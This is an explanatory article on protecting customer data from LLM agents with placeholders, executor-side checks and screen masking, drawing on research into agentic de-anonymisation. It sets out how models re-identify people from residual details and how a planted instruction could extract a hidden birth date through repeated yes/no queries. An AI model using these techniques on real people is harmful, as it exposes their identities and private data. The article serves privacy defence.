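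Encrypting the table helps only if the key is stored elsewhere. On 24 March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of LiteLLM, which were available for about 40 minutes. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) says the code searched for database passwords, cloud credentials and environment variables, which are settings that programs often use to store keys. A shop that kept its encryption key in such a variable could have had it stolen. Customers who ran LiteLLM's official container image were not affected because the image used fixed versions of its components.

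mcp-pvp keeps its values only in memory and discards them when the session ends, so a thief finds no archive of past customers. Hidet acknowledges that the vault offers no protection if someone takes over the machine. Nor can it stop a malicious tool from copying a value that the policy allows it to receive, so the shop still has to trust the courier with Maria's address.

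## Tasks that fail when the planner cannot see values

Placeholders work for moving Maria Keller's delivery because the planner only has to pass her address to the courier. Suppose she instead wants to hire a cello from a shop that hires only to adults. The planner then has to determine whether she is at least 18, which it can't do from BIRTHDATE_1, even if the executor restores values correctly.

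Tasks like this one differ in what the planner needs from the hidden value, and each need has its own remedy:

| The planner has to | Example | Remedy |
|---|---|---|
| Tell two people apart | Two customers are called Maria Keller | The executor compares a detail from the customer with the records |
| Compare or calculate | Is the customer at least 18? | The executor calculates and returns the result |
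| Notice a typo or mismatch | Maria writes her address as maria.keler@example.org | The executor checks the value on arrival and adds a warning |
| Infer something | The courier should phone at 9 am, her time | The executor supplies the time zone |
| Write fluent text | A letter should begin "Dear Ms Keller" | The executor fills in part of the name, or a local model edits the restored text |

### Two customers called Maria Keller

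If the shop has two customers in Leeds called Maria Keller, and one of them asks for a new delivery day without giving her email address, the agent has to search by name and town. Its next step depends on the results.

*What LLM Agents See and What Users Say* (Zhao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tests this situation on tau-bench, a benchmark in which agents serve the simulated customers of an online shop. One of the benchmark's tools looks up customers by name and postcode and returns only the first match, which works in the original data because no two customers share both. For 87 tasks in which the customer gives a postcode but no email address, the researchers added a second customer with the same name and postcode but a different street, email address and orders. Thirteen agents ran every task, and another language model played the customer.

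The researchers compared the original look-up with three others. A complete look-up returned every match, and a masked one did the same but hid part of the house number, as in "7** Park Avenue". The third, a street check, returned an error requiring the street address if several customers matched, and it released an account only when the street was right.

The results below are for simulated customers who knew their street and gave it when asked. Each look-up result is based on at least 1,131 conversations.

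| Look-up | Agent changed the wrong account | Agent revealed the other customer's data | Agent named the other customer's street | Task completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Only one customer exists | – | – | – | 66.0% |
| First match, wrong customer first | 25.8% | 92.0% | 28.1% | 11.8% |
| Every match | 4.2% | 30.1% | 11.1% | 54.9% |
| Every match, partly masked | 0.9% | 7.6% | 63.7% | 64.5% |
| Street check | 0% | 0% | 0% | 66.5% |

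With the original look-up, the agents nearly always assumed the first record was the customer's. In about a quarter of conversations, they then changed the wrong person's account, for example by cancelling an order, mostly without questioning whose account it was. They never made this mistake when the right customer came first, so the outcome depended on the order in which the database stored the two people.

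Newer models did little better. Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6.1 sol changed the wrong account in 18 of 80 conversations, because the look-up result gave no sign of a second customer. When the look-up returned every match, neither model made the mistake.

The masked listing nearly eliminated wrong-account changes, but agents now leaked data when they asked the customer which record was right, because they listed the candidate records with their street names. They named the other customer's street in nearly two thirds of the conversations where the customer's own records did not contain it. Of the two newer models, Claude Opus 5.5 did this in 1 of 37 conversations and GPT-6.1 sol in 31 of 37.

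Placeholders can cause the same leak. If the planner asks Maria whether she lives at ADDRESS_1 or ADDRESS_2, an executor that restores every placeholder in a reply will show her the other Maria's address. The recipient check therefore has to cover replies to the user as well as tool calls.

The street check avoids this because the agent never receives the other record. If the customer is truthful, the design guarantees its zeros. The informative result is that agents completed as many tasks as they did with only one customer. The experiment doesn't show how much of the benefit came from asking for the right detail and how much from withholding the records. Anyone who knows Maria's street could pass the check, so the shop still needs a way to confirm who is writing.

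The check works well with placeholders. Maria types her street, the planner sees ADDRESS_1 and passes it to the look-up, and the executor replaces it there with the street she typed. Zhao and colleagues' version also accepts the house number followed by the first word of the street name, so "14 Linden St" would match "14 Linden Street".

Look-ups that silently return one record seem to be uncommon outside benchmarks. In a hand-picked sample of 418 look-up tools, the researchers found only four clear cases, three of them in benchmarks. More often, a tool cut off a long list without indicating that more records existed. Outside the benchmarks, about 40% of the tools that limited their results did this, but nearly all of them returned at least ten records first and would have listed both Marias.

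### Why a warning in the prompt cannot help

Zhao and colleagues prove that there is a limit to how well a developer can solve the problem by telling the planner to watch out for customers with the same name.

Suppose two shops are identical except that one has a single customer named Maria Keller and the other has two, and that every look-up available to the planner returns the same text in both. The planner starts from the same request, so each possible first step has the same probability in both shops. The look-up then returns the same text, so the same is true of each later step until the planner asks the customer something. The probability that the planner moves a delivery before asking the customer anything is therefore the same in both shops.

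If the look-ups differ a little, the two probabilities can differ a little:

|P(acts, one Maria) − P(acts, two Marias)| ≤ *d*

Here *d* is the total variation distance, the most that the probability of any set of possible transcripts can differ between the two shops. If *d* is 0.05 and the planner acts 96% of the time in the shop with one Maria, it acts at least 91% of the time in the shop with two.

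A warning in the prompt only changes how the planner reacts to the text it reads. If that text is the same in both shops, the warning prevents exactly as many correct actions in the first shop as wrong ones in the second. To do better, the planner needs new information, either from the customer or from an added look-up such as the street check.

In one test, the researchers added a note to the look-up's result that other customers might match, and a rule that such a result does not establish who the customer is. The two newer models stopped changing the wrong accounts, but the added caution also kept them from changing the right ones. With only one customer in the database, their completed tasks fell from 67 of 80 to 2.

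If a planner sees the placeholder EMAIL_1 whether the email address is correct or misspelt, and nothing else in its context differs, no instruction can make it flag misspelt addresses more often than correct ones.

The executor needs very little information to resolve a tie between matching records, though the amount depends on the model. In a separate set of simple tasks, such as cancelling a named passenger's flight, 36 older agents acted in 79% of runs when the search showed only the first of two matching records. They acted in 54% when it also stated that there were two, and in 20% when it listed both. Claude Opus 5.5, GPT-6.1 sol and GPT-6 astra never acted when they received the count, because they opened the second record first. Without a count or a note, they acted in at least 93% of runs.

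### Typos and contradictions

A planner that read "Maria Keller, maria.keler@example.org" could notice that the email address is missing an "l" and ask about it. If it sees only the placeholders NAME_1 and EMAIL_1, it can only report that it found no order.

The executor can check a value for errors when it first arrives. It can verify a card number's check digit, compare a postcode with the town, or compare the spelling of an email address with the customer's name. If it finds a possible error, it passes the placeholder to the planner with a short warning, such as "EMAIL_1, possible misspelling". The warning shouldn't reveal that a similar address is on file, because a stranger could use that to find out who is a customer.

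Sometimes the user's statement conflicts with a record. Zhao and colleagues tested requests such as deleting a folder that the user describes as empty but that contains one item. They report results for the 27 agents that reliably carried out the request when the statement was true. When it was false, these agents went ahead in 28% of runs if the record gave only the number of items, and in 29% if it listed the item. When the user had not claimed that the folder was empty, the agents went ahead in about two thirds of runs with either kind of record.

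A count worked about as well as the contents, which is encouraging for placeholder designs. If Maria asks the shop to close her account because she has no open orders, `open_orders: 1` should be enough to make the planner stop without seeing the order itself. The researchers did not formally test whether the two rates were equal, and the tasks used only 16 templates, so the result is better evidence for the pattern than for the exact figures.

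### Calculations

A planner cannot subtract one hidden date from another or find the collection point nearest to ADDRESS_1. Designs that hide whole tool outputs, such as CaMeL and FIDES, also fail at some tasks where the planner must read a result before continuing.

The executor should handle sums, sorting and distances anyway, since ordinary code is more reliable at arithmetic than a language model. The planner specifies the calculation and the executor runs it on the real values. If the result is only needed for another tool call, the planner doesn't need to read it. For example, when Maria asks for the nearest collection point, the executor can find it, label it LOCATION_1 and send it straight to the courier.

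The planner must read a result that determines its next step. In the hire agreement, "at least 18" leads to a contract, and "under 18" leads to a request for a parent's signature.

### Time zones, titles and wording

Language models, like people, implicitly draw conclusions from names and addresses. If Maria asks the courier to phone at 9 am, a planner that can read "Leeds" in the address will assume British time, but one that sees only ADDRESS_1 has to guess or ask. The executor can add the time zone to the placeholder, which discloses little about someone in Leeds because millions of people share it. Better still, the phone tool can accept "9 am, recipient's time" and convert it internally, so the provider learns nothing more.

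Titles such as Mr and Ms are different because a name is poor evidence for them. Andrea is usually a man's name in Italy and a woman's in Germany, so a planner that sees the name may confidently choose the wrong title. Hiding the name may prevent this mistake. The shop should store the title the customer has chosen, or greet the customer by full name.

To write "Dear Ms Keller", the planner also needs a placeholder for the surname alone, since NAME_1 would give "Dear Ms Maria Keller". The executor can provide separate placeholders for the parts of a name, much as PrivacyGuard does for addresses.

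A message that fits the 160-character limit of a single text when the planner writes it may be too long once the executor restores the address, since ADDRESS_1 has 9 characters and "14 Linden Street, Leeds" has 23. The executor can give the planner each value's length or return the finished text's length before sending. In languages where names change their endings, a local model can correct the restored sentence, but someone should check the result because the planner never sees it.

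### Masked screens

When an agent works from screenshots, a private value is often also what it needs to click. To open a chat with Bob, for example, it has to find Bob's name on the screen.

Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *GUIGuard*, measured how hiding private data affected performance on MobileWorld, a benchmark of live phone tasks. One model found the private regions, and the software covered them with black boxes. A version of Gemini 3 then planned the steps, and a third model carried them out on the screen. The researchers classed names and phone numbers as high-risk, chat messages and schedules as medium-risk, and search suggestions as low-risk.

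| What the software covered | Share of information covered | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing | – | 55.6% |
| High-risk data | 3.0% | 41.6% |
| High- and medium-risk data | 11.9% | 7.5% |
| All private data | 48.0% | 3.3% |
| All private data except what the task needed | 25.5% | 8.1% |

The last row is surprising because an agent that can see everything it needs should do nearly as well as one working without masks. Wang and colleagues mainly blame the detector, which missed some private regions and covered other things the agent needed. The experiment therefore shows the combined effect of masking and poor detection. In similar tests with a different agent on AndroidWorld, another set of live phone tasks, covering medium-risk data again reduced performance the most.

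Masking had looked far less harmful in a test of single steps. The researchers compared the plans that Gemini 3 Pro wrote for masked screenshots with its plans for the originals, and a judge model scored their agreement at 3.35 out of 4. One mistake could not lead to another in this test because it used recorded sessions and showed the planner the next recorded screenshot whatever it had just proposed.

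Clicking the right place also becomes harder. On 970 Android screenshots, Gemini 3.1 Pro picked the correct spot in 97.9% of cases without masks and 77.5% with black boxes. If a task took ten such clicks, with independent errors and no second attempts, the chance of completing it would be

0.979¹⁰ ≈ 81% without masks and 0.775¹⁰ ≈ 8% with them.

Real agents can often recover from a wrong click, so this exaggerates the loss, but it shows how a moderate error rate per step can make a long task fail.

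### Showing only what the task needs

*CAPED* starts from the task instead of the private data. Software on the phone turns the user's instruction into a short list of requirements, each with an app, a subject and its type. "Send a beach photo to Bob" would require a beach photo from the gallery and a person called Bob in the messaging app. A match in one app doesn't give access to similar content in another.

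The software then chooses a default for each screen. It leaves settings pages visible, hides the pictures in a gallery, and hides both text and pictures in chats and contact lists. Next, it uncovers the elements that match a requirement. It compares text by words and meaning, and uses a vision model to check whether a picture shows the right subject. Names that the planner needs appear as typed placeholders, which are the same in the instruction and on the screen. If the agent tries to tap a covered region, the software can ask the user to reveal it for that one action.

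The evaluation used 28 tasks with planted private facts. A judge model examined the screenshots the provider would receive and tried to infer facts that the task did not need, with more sensitive facts weighted more heavily. The leak rates cover only runs in which the agent fully completed its task, so a method gets no credit for runs that failed before reaching the private screens.

| Protection | Irrelevant private facts leaked | Average task score (0 to 1) |
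|---|---|---|
| None | 76.6% | 0.893 |
| Placeholders for text only | 75.2% | 0.911 |
| Screen defaults without task requirements | 2.8% | 0.321 |
| Full system | 26.8% | 0.929 |

Replacing only text protected almost nothing, because photos, product recommendations and health displays still revealed most of the planted facts. Hiding content by screen type leaked very little but made most tasks fail. The full system did best when the user named a specific target. It has to show much more for a request such as "the latest receipt", because it cannot determine in advance which item is meant.

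On 116 ordinary AndroidWorld tasks, the agent completed 77 without protection and 64 with it. Nineteen tasks succeeded only without protection, and six succeeded only with it. The researchers attributed six of the 19 failures mainly to faults in the test environment or the apps, found six more to be recoverable in diagnostic runs, and linked the remaining seven to the protection. The altered screenshots more often sent the agent along a different route or led it to use up its allowed steps, and a covered button was seldom the main cause.

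These results are much better than MobileWorld's, but the agents and tasks differ, so the gap doesn't measure the benefit of selective exposure. The protection also took time, as the agent's own work accounted for 8.0 of the 10.8 seconds in an average step.

### A company that switched masking off

At least one large vendor, Salesforce, has decided that its agents need to see the values. It has disabled masking for Agentforce, its platform for AI agents, according to its *LLM Data Masking* and two of its training pages, *Explore LLM Data Masking* and *Meet the Einstein Trust Layer*. Masking remains available for built-in features such as drafting replies to customers, and developers can use it when they call a model from their own code, as Salesforce's *Access Models API with Apex* explains.

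The company says that masking slows the agent down and interferes with its planning and actions, and that many customers reported less accurate answers, but it publishes no figures. It gives the example of an agent that has to look up a customer record and list similar accounts, which the agent cannot do without knowing what the first account is like.

That task is a comparison, so an executor could handle it:

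```
find_similar(account="ACCOUNT_1", by=["industry", "size"])
```

However, a developer has to anticipate that someone will want to compare accounts by industry and size. The developer of a cello shop's agent with three tools can do this, but developers of a platform whose customers invent their own tasks cannot foresee every comparison, which makes Salesforce's choice easier to understand.

Instead of masking, the company relies on agreements that forbid model providers from keeping its customers' data, and on rules about what each agent may read and do. It also announced plans to run Anthropic's Claude models inside its own network. These measures limit what a provider can keep, but the planner still reads the real values.

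### Letting the executor answer questions

In most of the shop's examples, the planner needs one fact about a value rather than the value itself. The executor can offer tools that return such facts:

| Planner's call | Answer |
|---|---|
| `is_at_least(BIRTHDATE_1, years=18)` | true |
| `matches_order(ADDRESS_1, order="58213")` | true |
| `time_zone(ADDRESS_1)` | Europe/London |

FIDES can get similarly short answers from a quarantined model. Ordinary code is better where it can do the job, because it gives the same answer every time and doesn't follow instructions hidden in the data.

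However, every answer reveals some information, and this adds up. Suppose the planner can ask whether BIRTHDATE_1 falls before any date it chooses, and the provider knows only that Maria was born between 1926 and 2025, a period of 36,525 days. Asking whether she was born before 1 January 1976 leaves at most 18,263 possible days, whichever answer comes back. A second question can reduce that to at most 9,132, and each further question can roughly halve the remainder.

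With *k* yes-or-no questions there are 2ᵏ possible sequences of answers. To single out any one of the 36,525 days, the planner needs at least that many sequences:

2¹⁵ = 32,768 < 36,525 ≤ 65,536 = 2¹⁶

It takes 16 questions to guarantee finding the exact date, 17 for a salary in whole pounds below £100,000, and eight for a house number between 1 and 200. A planner has no legitimate reason to ask so many questions, but a planted instruction could make it ask them through a series of calls that each look harmless.

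Equality questions reveal much less when there are many possible values. "Was she born on 3 May 1981?" usually rules out only one day, so finding the date this way would take more than 18,000 guesses on average. Equality questions offer little protection when the hidden value is a town, where a few guesses may be enough, or when the attacker already has a short list of candidates.

The shop can limit what is disclosed by fixing in advance which questions the planner can ask. If the planner can ask only whether a customer is at least 18, repeating the question on the same day reveals nothing new. But asking it daily can disclose the customer's birthday, because the answer changes from "no" to "yes" on the day the customer turns 18. The executor can prevent this by answering only when there is a hire agreement to sign.

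If the planner has to choose its own thresholds, the executor should count the answers it gives about each value. After three yes-or-no answers, the chance of guessing Maria's exact birth date is at most 8 in 36,525, assuming all dates were equally likely at the start. The count has to continue across sessions, or the planner could get three more answers in Maria's next conversation. The shop can store the count with her internal record number, where the provider cannot see it.

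### A local model, the user or the real value

Some questions have no ready-made function. For those, the shop can use a local model, ask the customer, or show the planner the value. For the hire agreement, the choices compare like this:

| Who settles whether Maria is an adult | What the provider receives | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Executor | "At least 18" | A developer must have foreseen the question |
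| Local model | Whatever the model returns | It may be wrong, and the planner cannot check |
| Maria | Her reply, with placeholders | She has to answer, and her answer may be false |
| Planner, from the real value | Her full birth date | The provider may keep the date |

A local model works well for tasks on free text, such as deciding whether a delivery note contains a complaint. Where possible, the executor should allow the model only a few fixed answers and count them, as it does with code.

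Asking the user is best when the agent is unsure what the user wants. Zhao and colleagues propose a general standard for agents that act on someone's behalf. Before acting, the agent should verify its assumptions or have the user settle them. Otherwise, it should tell the user about the doubt while the action can still be undone. Older agents rarely gave such warnings. When the researchers gave 13 of them an undo tool, several acted more readily. However, of the 12 that acted on one of two matching records, 11 warned the user in at most half of those runs.

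The agent also has to ask a question whose answer shows which account is the customer's. In the shop tests, the two newer models made 14 changes to a wrong account after questioning whose it was. In ten of these cases, the customer's reply could not have distinguished the two accounts, and in the other four, the customer told the agent to continue with an account it had described as verified. If two customers are both named Maria Keller, the agent needs to ask for something that differs between them, such as their street address, rather than confirm the name.

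Showing the planner the real value is reasonable when the task depends on details that nobody can list in advance. If Maria wants help with a letter disputing a courier's account of where her parcel went, the planner may need the street, the house number and the neighbour's address together. The application resends the conversation with every request, so the provider would keep receiving these details after the letter was finished. To prevent this, the shop can have the executor put the placeholders back as soon as the planner finishes the letter, including in the planner's own text. The provider then receives the address in only one or two requests.

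## Identifying people from the details that remain

Even if the detector catches all of Maria Keller's direct identifiers, the model provider may be able to identify her from the quasi-identifiers that remain. These show that she teaches, has bought a cello and lives near the Leeds South depot.

### How details multiply

Leeds has roughly 800,000 inhabitants. Suppose Maria's messages reveal that she is a music teacher in her forties with a chronic back condition, and that these details are as common as the table assumes:

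| What the provider knows | Share of residents | People left |
|---|---|---|
| She lives in the city | – | 800,000 |
| She is a music teacher | 1 in 2,000 | 400 |
| She is in her forties | 1 in 10 | 40 |
| She has a back condition | 1 in 50 | 0.8 |

If the details are independent of each other, the expected number of matches is

800,000 × 1/2,000 × 1/10 × 1/50 = 0.8

Maria certainly exists, so the provider should expect about 0.8 other people to match. The number of others roughly follows a Poisson distribution, the usual model for counts of rare events, so the chance that nobody else matches is e^(−0.8), or about 45%. A provider that picked at random from a list of everyone who matches would choose Maria about 69% of the time.

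Real details are rarely independent, so each share should be calculated among the people who match the earlier details. Music teachers lift instruments and sit for hours, so perhaps one in ten of them has a back condition, which would leave four expected matches instead of 0.8. Dependence can also make someone easier to find. If one resident in ten is a teenager but only one music teacher in 200 is, the expected number of matches for a teenage music teacher with the condition in the table is 0.04. Some details add almost nothing, such as owning a cello when the provider already knows that the person teaches the cello.

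Even when only one person matches the details, the provider can't identify that person without a source that connects the details to a name. Many music teachers advertise online, but nobody publishes a list of which ones have back conditions, so the provider might only be able to narrow the search to 40 names.

*Large-scale online deanonymization with LLMs* (Lermen, Swanson and colleagues, 2026) cites an older result that postcode, date of birth and sex are enough to single out 87% of the US population. It also cites an earlier study of mobile phone records, in which four points in place and time were enough to single out 95% of the people.

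### What language models can do with a description

The effort of identifying people from the remaining details used to protect most of them, because someone had to read the text, decide which details mattered and search for a person who fitted them. Lermen and colleagues tested how much of this work a language model with web search can do. They summarised the posts of 338 users of the forum Hacker News who had linked to their own LinkedIn profiles, and removed names, links and other direct identifiers. The model correctly named 226 of the users (67%) and gave a wrong name for 25. Each attempt cost between one and four dollars.

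They then ran larger tests without web search, using software to match each person to one entry in a fixed pool. One model summarised what each person had written, a search found similar summaries, and other models compared the best candidates and either chose one or gave no answer. The results below are at 90% precision, and recall is the share of people matched correctly.

| Task | Size of pool | Recall |
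|---|---|---|
| Match a LinkedIn profile to a Hacker News account | 1,000 | 68.3% |
| The same, with more candidates | 89,000 | 55.2% |
| Match earlier and later comments by one Reddit user | 10,000 | 67.3% |
| Match one user's film comments in different Reddit communities | 9,781 | 8.5% |

People who link their accounts publicly probably reveal more about themselves than people who want to stay anonymous, so the first two rows may overstate the risk to others. Everyone in these tests also had a match in the pool. In practice, most of the shop's customers may be missing from whatever list the provider uses, which would lower precision.

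Suppose the software correctly matches 50% of the people who are on the list, mismatches 5% of them, and wrongly matches 1% of the people who are not on it. If everyone is on the list, 91% of its matches are correct. If only one person in 100 is on it, the figure is

0.01 × 0.50 ÷ (0.01 × 0.50 + 0.01 × 0.05 + 0.99 × 0.01) ≈ 32%

An attacker can reduce false matches by accepting only the most certain ones. Lermen and colleagues calculate that, even if only one Reddit user in 10,000 had a match, their software could still find about 9% of the users who had one, and 90% of the matches it reported would be correct.

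### Interviews with the names removed

In December 2025, Anthropic published 1,250 interviews about how people use AI at work, after redacting some details. In *Agentic LLMs as Powerful Deanonymizers*, Li (2026) examined the 125 interviews with scientists. A model classified 24 of them as discussing published work, and a second model searched the web for that work. Li checked the best matches by hand and accepted six. Each attempt took about four minutes and cost less than 50 cents.

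A match to a paper with several authors narrows the search to a small group, while a match to a dissertation identifies one person. Li reported the findings to Anthropic a day after the release. The company replied that the participants had agreed to publication of the raw transcripts, and called the redaction "an additional courtesy, not a privacy safeguard".

Lermen and colleagues later tried to identify the scientists in 33 of the interviews and judged nine identifications to be correct. Neither study could confirm its matches, because nobody outside Anthropic knows who the participants were. Scientists are also unusually easy to find, since they publish detailed descriptions of their work. *AGENTDOXX* (Wen and Li, 2026) extended the search to all 1,250 interviews and found 43 matches (3.4%) that passed several rounds of checks.

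To check models' answers against known identities, Wen and Li generated 822 synthetic interviews based on public facts about real people who had answered questions on Reddit under their own names. They removed direct identifiers and asked models to name each person. The five best configurations named the right person in 47% to 48% of cases.

Without web search, three open models still named 15% to 28% of the people from what they had learned in training. With search, two of them, Kimi K3 and GLM-5.3 Flash, were among the five best. Success with search depended mainly on finding the right page. When the person's name appeared in a search result, the models identified them 91% of the time, but even the best configuration's searches returned the name for only 53% of the interviews.

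The models' confidence ratings were also fairly reliable. Among the six strongest configurations with search, 18% to 45% of all proposed names were correct, compared with 89% to 97% of those the models marked as high-confidence.

Everyone in this collection had a public presence and had talked about themselves online, so the percentages don't apply to the general population. A well-known cellist who orders from the shop risks being identified even by a planner without web access, while a private customer with no website is much harder to identify.

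### A provider that knows how Maria writes

The model provider may be able to identify Maria from its own records, without searching the web. If she also uses the provider's chatbot, the provider may have months of her messages under her name. It could compare these with the shop's messages about her, even though those arrive under the shop's account.

The linking attacks by Pham and colleagues model a similar situation, in which people send prompts through a service that hides their account and network address. The attacks worked on short texts. Users wrote 45 words in a typical conversation in the chat collection and 58 in the coding collection, compared with 335 words per post in an older study of anonymous blogs.

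Among chat users, the attacks found up to 10% of the people in the provider's records and wrongly matched up to 10% of everyone else. Suppose 1,000 customers write to the shop and the provider has records on 100 of them. At those rates, it would correctly match up to ten of the 100 and wrongly match up to 90 of the other 900, so a match would be only a lead to follow up. A stricter threshold would produce fewer false matches but also fewer correct ones.

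A larger archive did not necessarily help the attacker, because it also contained more people to confuse with the right one. Re-ranking the matches with a language model did not improve the results in early tests.

Pham and colleagues also tried adding text designed to make the attacker's software misjudge a conversation's topic. This made it harder to group anonymous conversations by author, but barely changed how many users the attacks identified. An attacker who knew about the trick could also look for the added text and remove it.

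### From interviews to orders

None of these studies tested customer-service transcripts, which differ from interviews in two ways that have opposite effects on how easily people can be identified. First, customers say less about themselves. Anthropic's interviewer asked scientists to describe a recent project from the first idea to the final result, while Maria writes two sentences about a delivery.

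In the Reddit film test, users were easier to identify the more they had written. Lermen and colleagues identified 3.1% of users who had mentioned only one film in both sets of comments, and 48.1% of those who had mentioned ten or more. By this measure, a year of conversations with a personal assistant reveals far more about a person than a single delivery does.

The second difference is that agent transcripts contain exact dates, places and products, which are easier to match than opinions. *From Weak Cues to Real Identities* repeats a well-known attack on film ratings that Netflix had published without names. An agent received a few of one person's ratings and had to find that person among 1,000 users. The researchers had shifted the dates by up to three weeks and changed about half of the ratings by one star. With two ratings, GPT-5 found the right person 79% of the time, compared with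 53% for Claude 4.5 and 56% to 60% for the original method. With four ratings, both models exceeded 90%.

Two dated orders could be just as revealing to someone with a matching list. The courier, unlike the public, has a list of cello deliveries. If the courier's agent sends unprotected data to the same model provider, the provider can use the shared order number to link ADDRESS_1 to 14 Linden Street. Without the order number, the provider could still compare the depot and delivery day, although many other parcels would share both.

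A personal assistant's history is more like a record of web searches. *From Weak Cues to Real Identities* also uses search histories that the internet company AOL released in 2006. The researchers selected 40 long histories with repeated searches about the same places, jobs or interests, and excluded any in which people had searched for their own names. An agent with web access identified ten people whom the researchers could confirm from public sources. These were promising cases, so the one-in-four success rate doesn't apply to search histories in general. But once a history is linked to a name, any searches in it about illness, debt or a family crisis are linked to that person too.

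### When the planner does the searching

A provider would have to study its logs deliberately to identify Maria, but a planner with a search tool might find her name during ordinary work. If the shop asks its agent to recommend sheet music for a customer who teaches the cello in Leeds, the agent might search for cello teachers there and open Maria's website. Her name would then be in the planner's context even though the executor never disclosed it, and the search company would also have received the details in the query.

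*From Weak Cues to Real Identities* tests whether agents connect records when they have not been asked to identify anyone. In each case, the agent received an anonymised source and a second source with overlapping details. When the task was harmless analysis, Claude 4.5 named the right person in 16 of 20 cases. When the researchers asked for the person's identity, GPT-5 succeeded in 19 of 20. A privacy instruction suppressed the behaviour but also made the agents worse at their tasks. Because the agents were given both sources, an agent without web access could do the same with a customer list and a folder of pseudonymised complaints.

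A model told not to identify people may also omit a name from its answer but leave it in the transcript. Wen and Li gave this instruction to 12 model configurations, using 143 interviews in which at least one of them had previously identified the interviewee. The average identification rate fell from 75.1% to 21.6%. However, in 37% of the cases where the model withheld the name, it had already retrieved it. Gemini 3.1 Pro never named the person but found the name in 62% of the interviews. The instruction hardly affected two models with little or no reasoning, and Llama 4 Maverick named slightly more people than before.

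The shop therefore needs to control the search tool itself. The executor can refuse queries that contain details about a customer, or run the search in a separate session that receives only a general question, such as which cello books suit beginners.

Replacing names in the search results can reveal who the placeholders stand for. If the planner opens Maria's website and the executor replaces her name there with NAME_1, the provider learns that NAME_1 owns the site. The provider also knows the site's address, so it can visit the site and read her name. Withholding the page is safer.

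### Leaving out the rarest detail

The calculation for Leeds also shows which detail is most worth removing:

| What the provider receives | Expected matches besides Maria |
|---|---|
| Music teacher, forties, back condition | 0.8 |
| Music teacher, back condition | 8 |
| Teacher (1 in 50), forties, back condition | 32 |
| Music teacher, forties | 40 |
| Forties, back condition | 1,600 |

Dropping Maria's occupation protects her identity far more than dropping her age. The planner needs neither detail to move a delivery, so the executor could shorten her message to a request for delivery on Thursday. When a customer asks for advice on an instrument, her occupation may matter, so the executor could keep it and drop her age and back condition instead.

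The difficulty is that details arrive one at a time. Panjwani (2026), in *CAMP*, proposes a running score for a conversation. Each type of personal data has a weight, such as 0.3 for an organisation, 0.5 for a location, 0.6 for a name, 0.8 for an email address and 0.85 for a medical condition. The score rises faster as more types appear together. The paper describes this with a graph that links every type to every other, but the result simplifies to

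score = sum of weights × (1 + 0.3 × (number of types − 1))

If Maria gives her name and email address, the score is 1.4 × 1.3 = 1.82. When she mentions Leeds in her next message, the score rises to 1.9 × 1.6 = 3.04. This exceeds the suggested limit of 2, so the software replaces her details with surrogates throughout the conversation, including in earlier messages.

By then, the provider has already received her real name and email address in the first request. Panjwani reports that CAMP reduced exposure to zero in all four test conversations, but that can only be true of the rewritten history, because the software first intervened between the second and fifth turns. An ordinary redaction proxy would have replaced the name immediately. A running score makes more sense as an addition to such a proxy, used to decide when the remaining details have become too specific.

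For that purpose, the weights would need to reflect how rare a value is. CAMP treats a village of 200 people and a city of 800,000 as the same kind of location. It also ignores details without a recognised type, such as Maria's cello and her teaching on Tuesdays. Its four conversations were synthetic and had at most ten turns each, so they don't show how well the score predicts actual identification.

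### Rewriting the context

Instead of counting details, software can look for the passages that identify someone and change them. Wen and Li compared several ways of doing this on the same 143 interviews:

| Change to the text | Average share of people identified |
|---|---|
| None | 75.1% |
| Mask names and other named entities | 62.0% |
| Mask them and paraphrase the rest | 45.9% |
| Remove identifying passages | 35.1% |
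| Replace identifying details with false ones | 34.2% |

Masking named entities, which is roughly what a placeholder system does, had the smallest effect. Kimi K3 still identified 85% of the people after masking. A phrase that combines a job, a project and a number of years may contain no named entities for a detector to find.

Wen and Li trained a small open model to remove identifying passages, using the details that earlier attacks had exploited. Inserting false details worked about as well, but the software that inserted them had a list of true facts about each person, which an executor would not normally have. Some attackers noticed that the false details contradicted the rest of the text, dismissed the contradictions as transcription errors and still found the right person.

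Li, Wen and Li (2026), in *LLM Anonymization Against Agentic Re-identification*, present a more elaborate method called AURA. A model with web search first looks for details that could identify this particular person, beyond a standard list that includes age, occupation and place of birth. A second model rewrites the text repeatedly until it can no longer infer those details. AURA then masks the passages that changed, generates several replacements for each, and leaves the rest of the text alone. It picks the version that reveals least, and if there is a tie, the one that loses the least useful content.

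Li and colleagues tested the method on 53 of Anthropic's interviews that they had previously traced to a person or a small group. Three models with web search then tried to trace them again. To measure how useful the interviews remained, the researchers took 4,758 pairs of facts, each combining a detail of the person's background with something they had said, and checked how many a reader could still recover.

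| Method | Interviews identified, of 53 | Fact pairs kept |
|---|---|---|
| Presidio | 26–40 | 95.6% |
| One rewrite, detailed instructions | 23–33 | 96.5% |
| One rewrite, brief instructions | 11–18 | 87.0% |
| Earlier method with repeated rewriting | 10–12 | 66.3% |
| AURA, with details chosen for each person | 0–7 | 72.0–76.1% |
| Random word replacement, strongest setting | 0 | 0% |

The last method offers a mathematical guarantee based on differential privacy, but at this setting it destroyed the text. AURA has no such guarantee, so a better attacker might identify more people.

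AURA suits research interviews better than live agents. Losing a quarter of the fact pairs may be acceptable in a study of attitudes to AI, but if the software changes "Thursday" to "later in the week", the courier can't book the delivery. The repeated rewriting would also delay every step, and the first stage sends queries about the person to a search engine, which would disclose some of the information the shop wants to hide. The shop could run that stage on a few synthetic conversations instead, to learn which kinds of detail its executor should remove.

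### Omitting, generalising or replacing

Maria may also want to hide something from the people her agent writes to. If she needs a day off to see a back specialist, the agent could omit the reason from its message to her employer, generalise it to "a health matter", or replace it with a different reason. *Say Something Else* (Xiao, Li and colleagues, 2026) compared these strategies in 792 scenarios with seven models. After the first message, a simulated recipient asked two follow-up questions. Another model then tried to guess the private facts from the conversation.

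Leakage in the table runs from 0 to 1, and guessing the right category counts as 0.5. The combined score is the share of information kept private multiplied by the usefulness of the messages.

| Strategy | Leakage | Combined score | Increase in exact guesses after follow-up |
|---|---|---|---|
| No protection | 0.29 | 0.694 | 6.2 points |
| Omit | 0.16 | 0.730 | 8.3 points |
| Generalise | 0.24 | 0.664 | 11.8 points |
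| Replace | 0.22 | 0.764 | 3.9 points |

Replacing the facts scored best overall because the messages remained almost as useful as unprotected ones. Omitting them leaked less but often left the recipient without an adequate answer. Generalising did worse than no protection on the combined score. A vague reply narrows the possibilities and invites further questions, and the models' answers to those questions tended to be closer to the truth.

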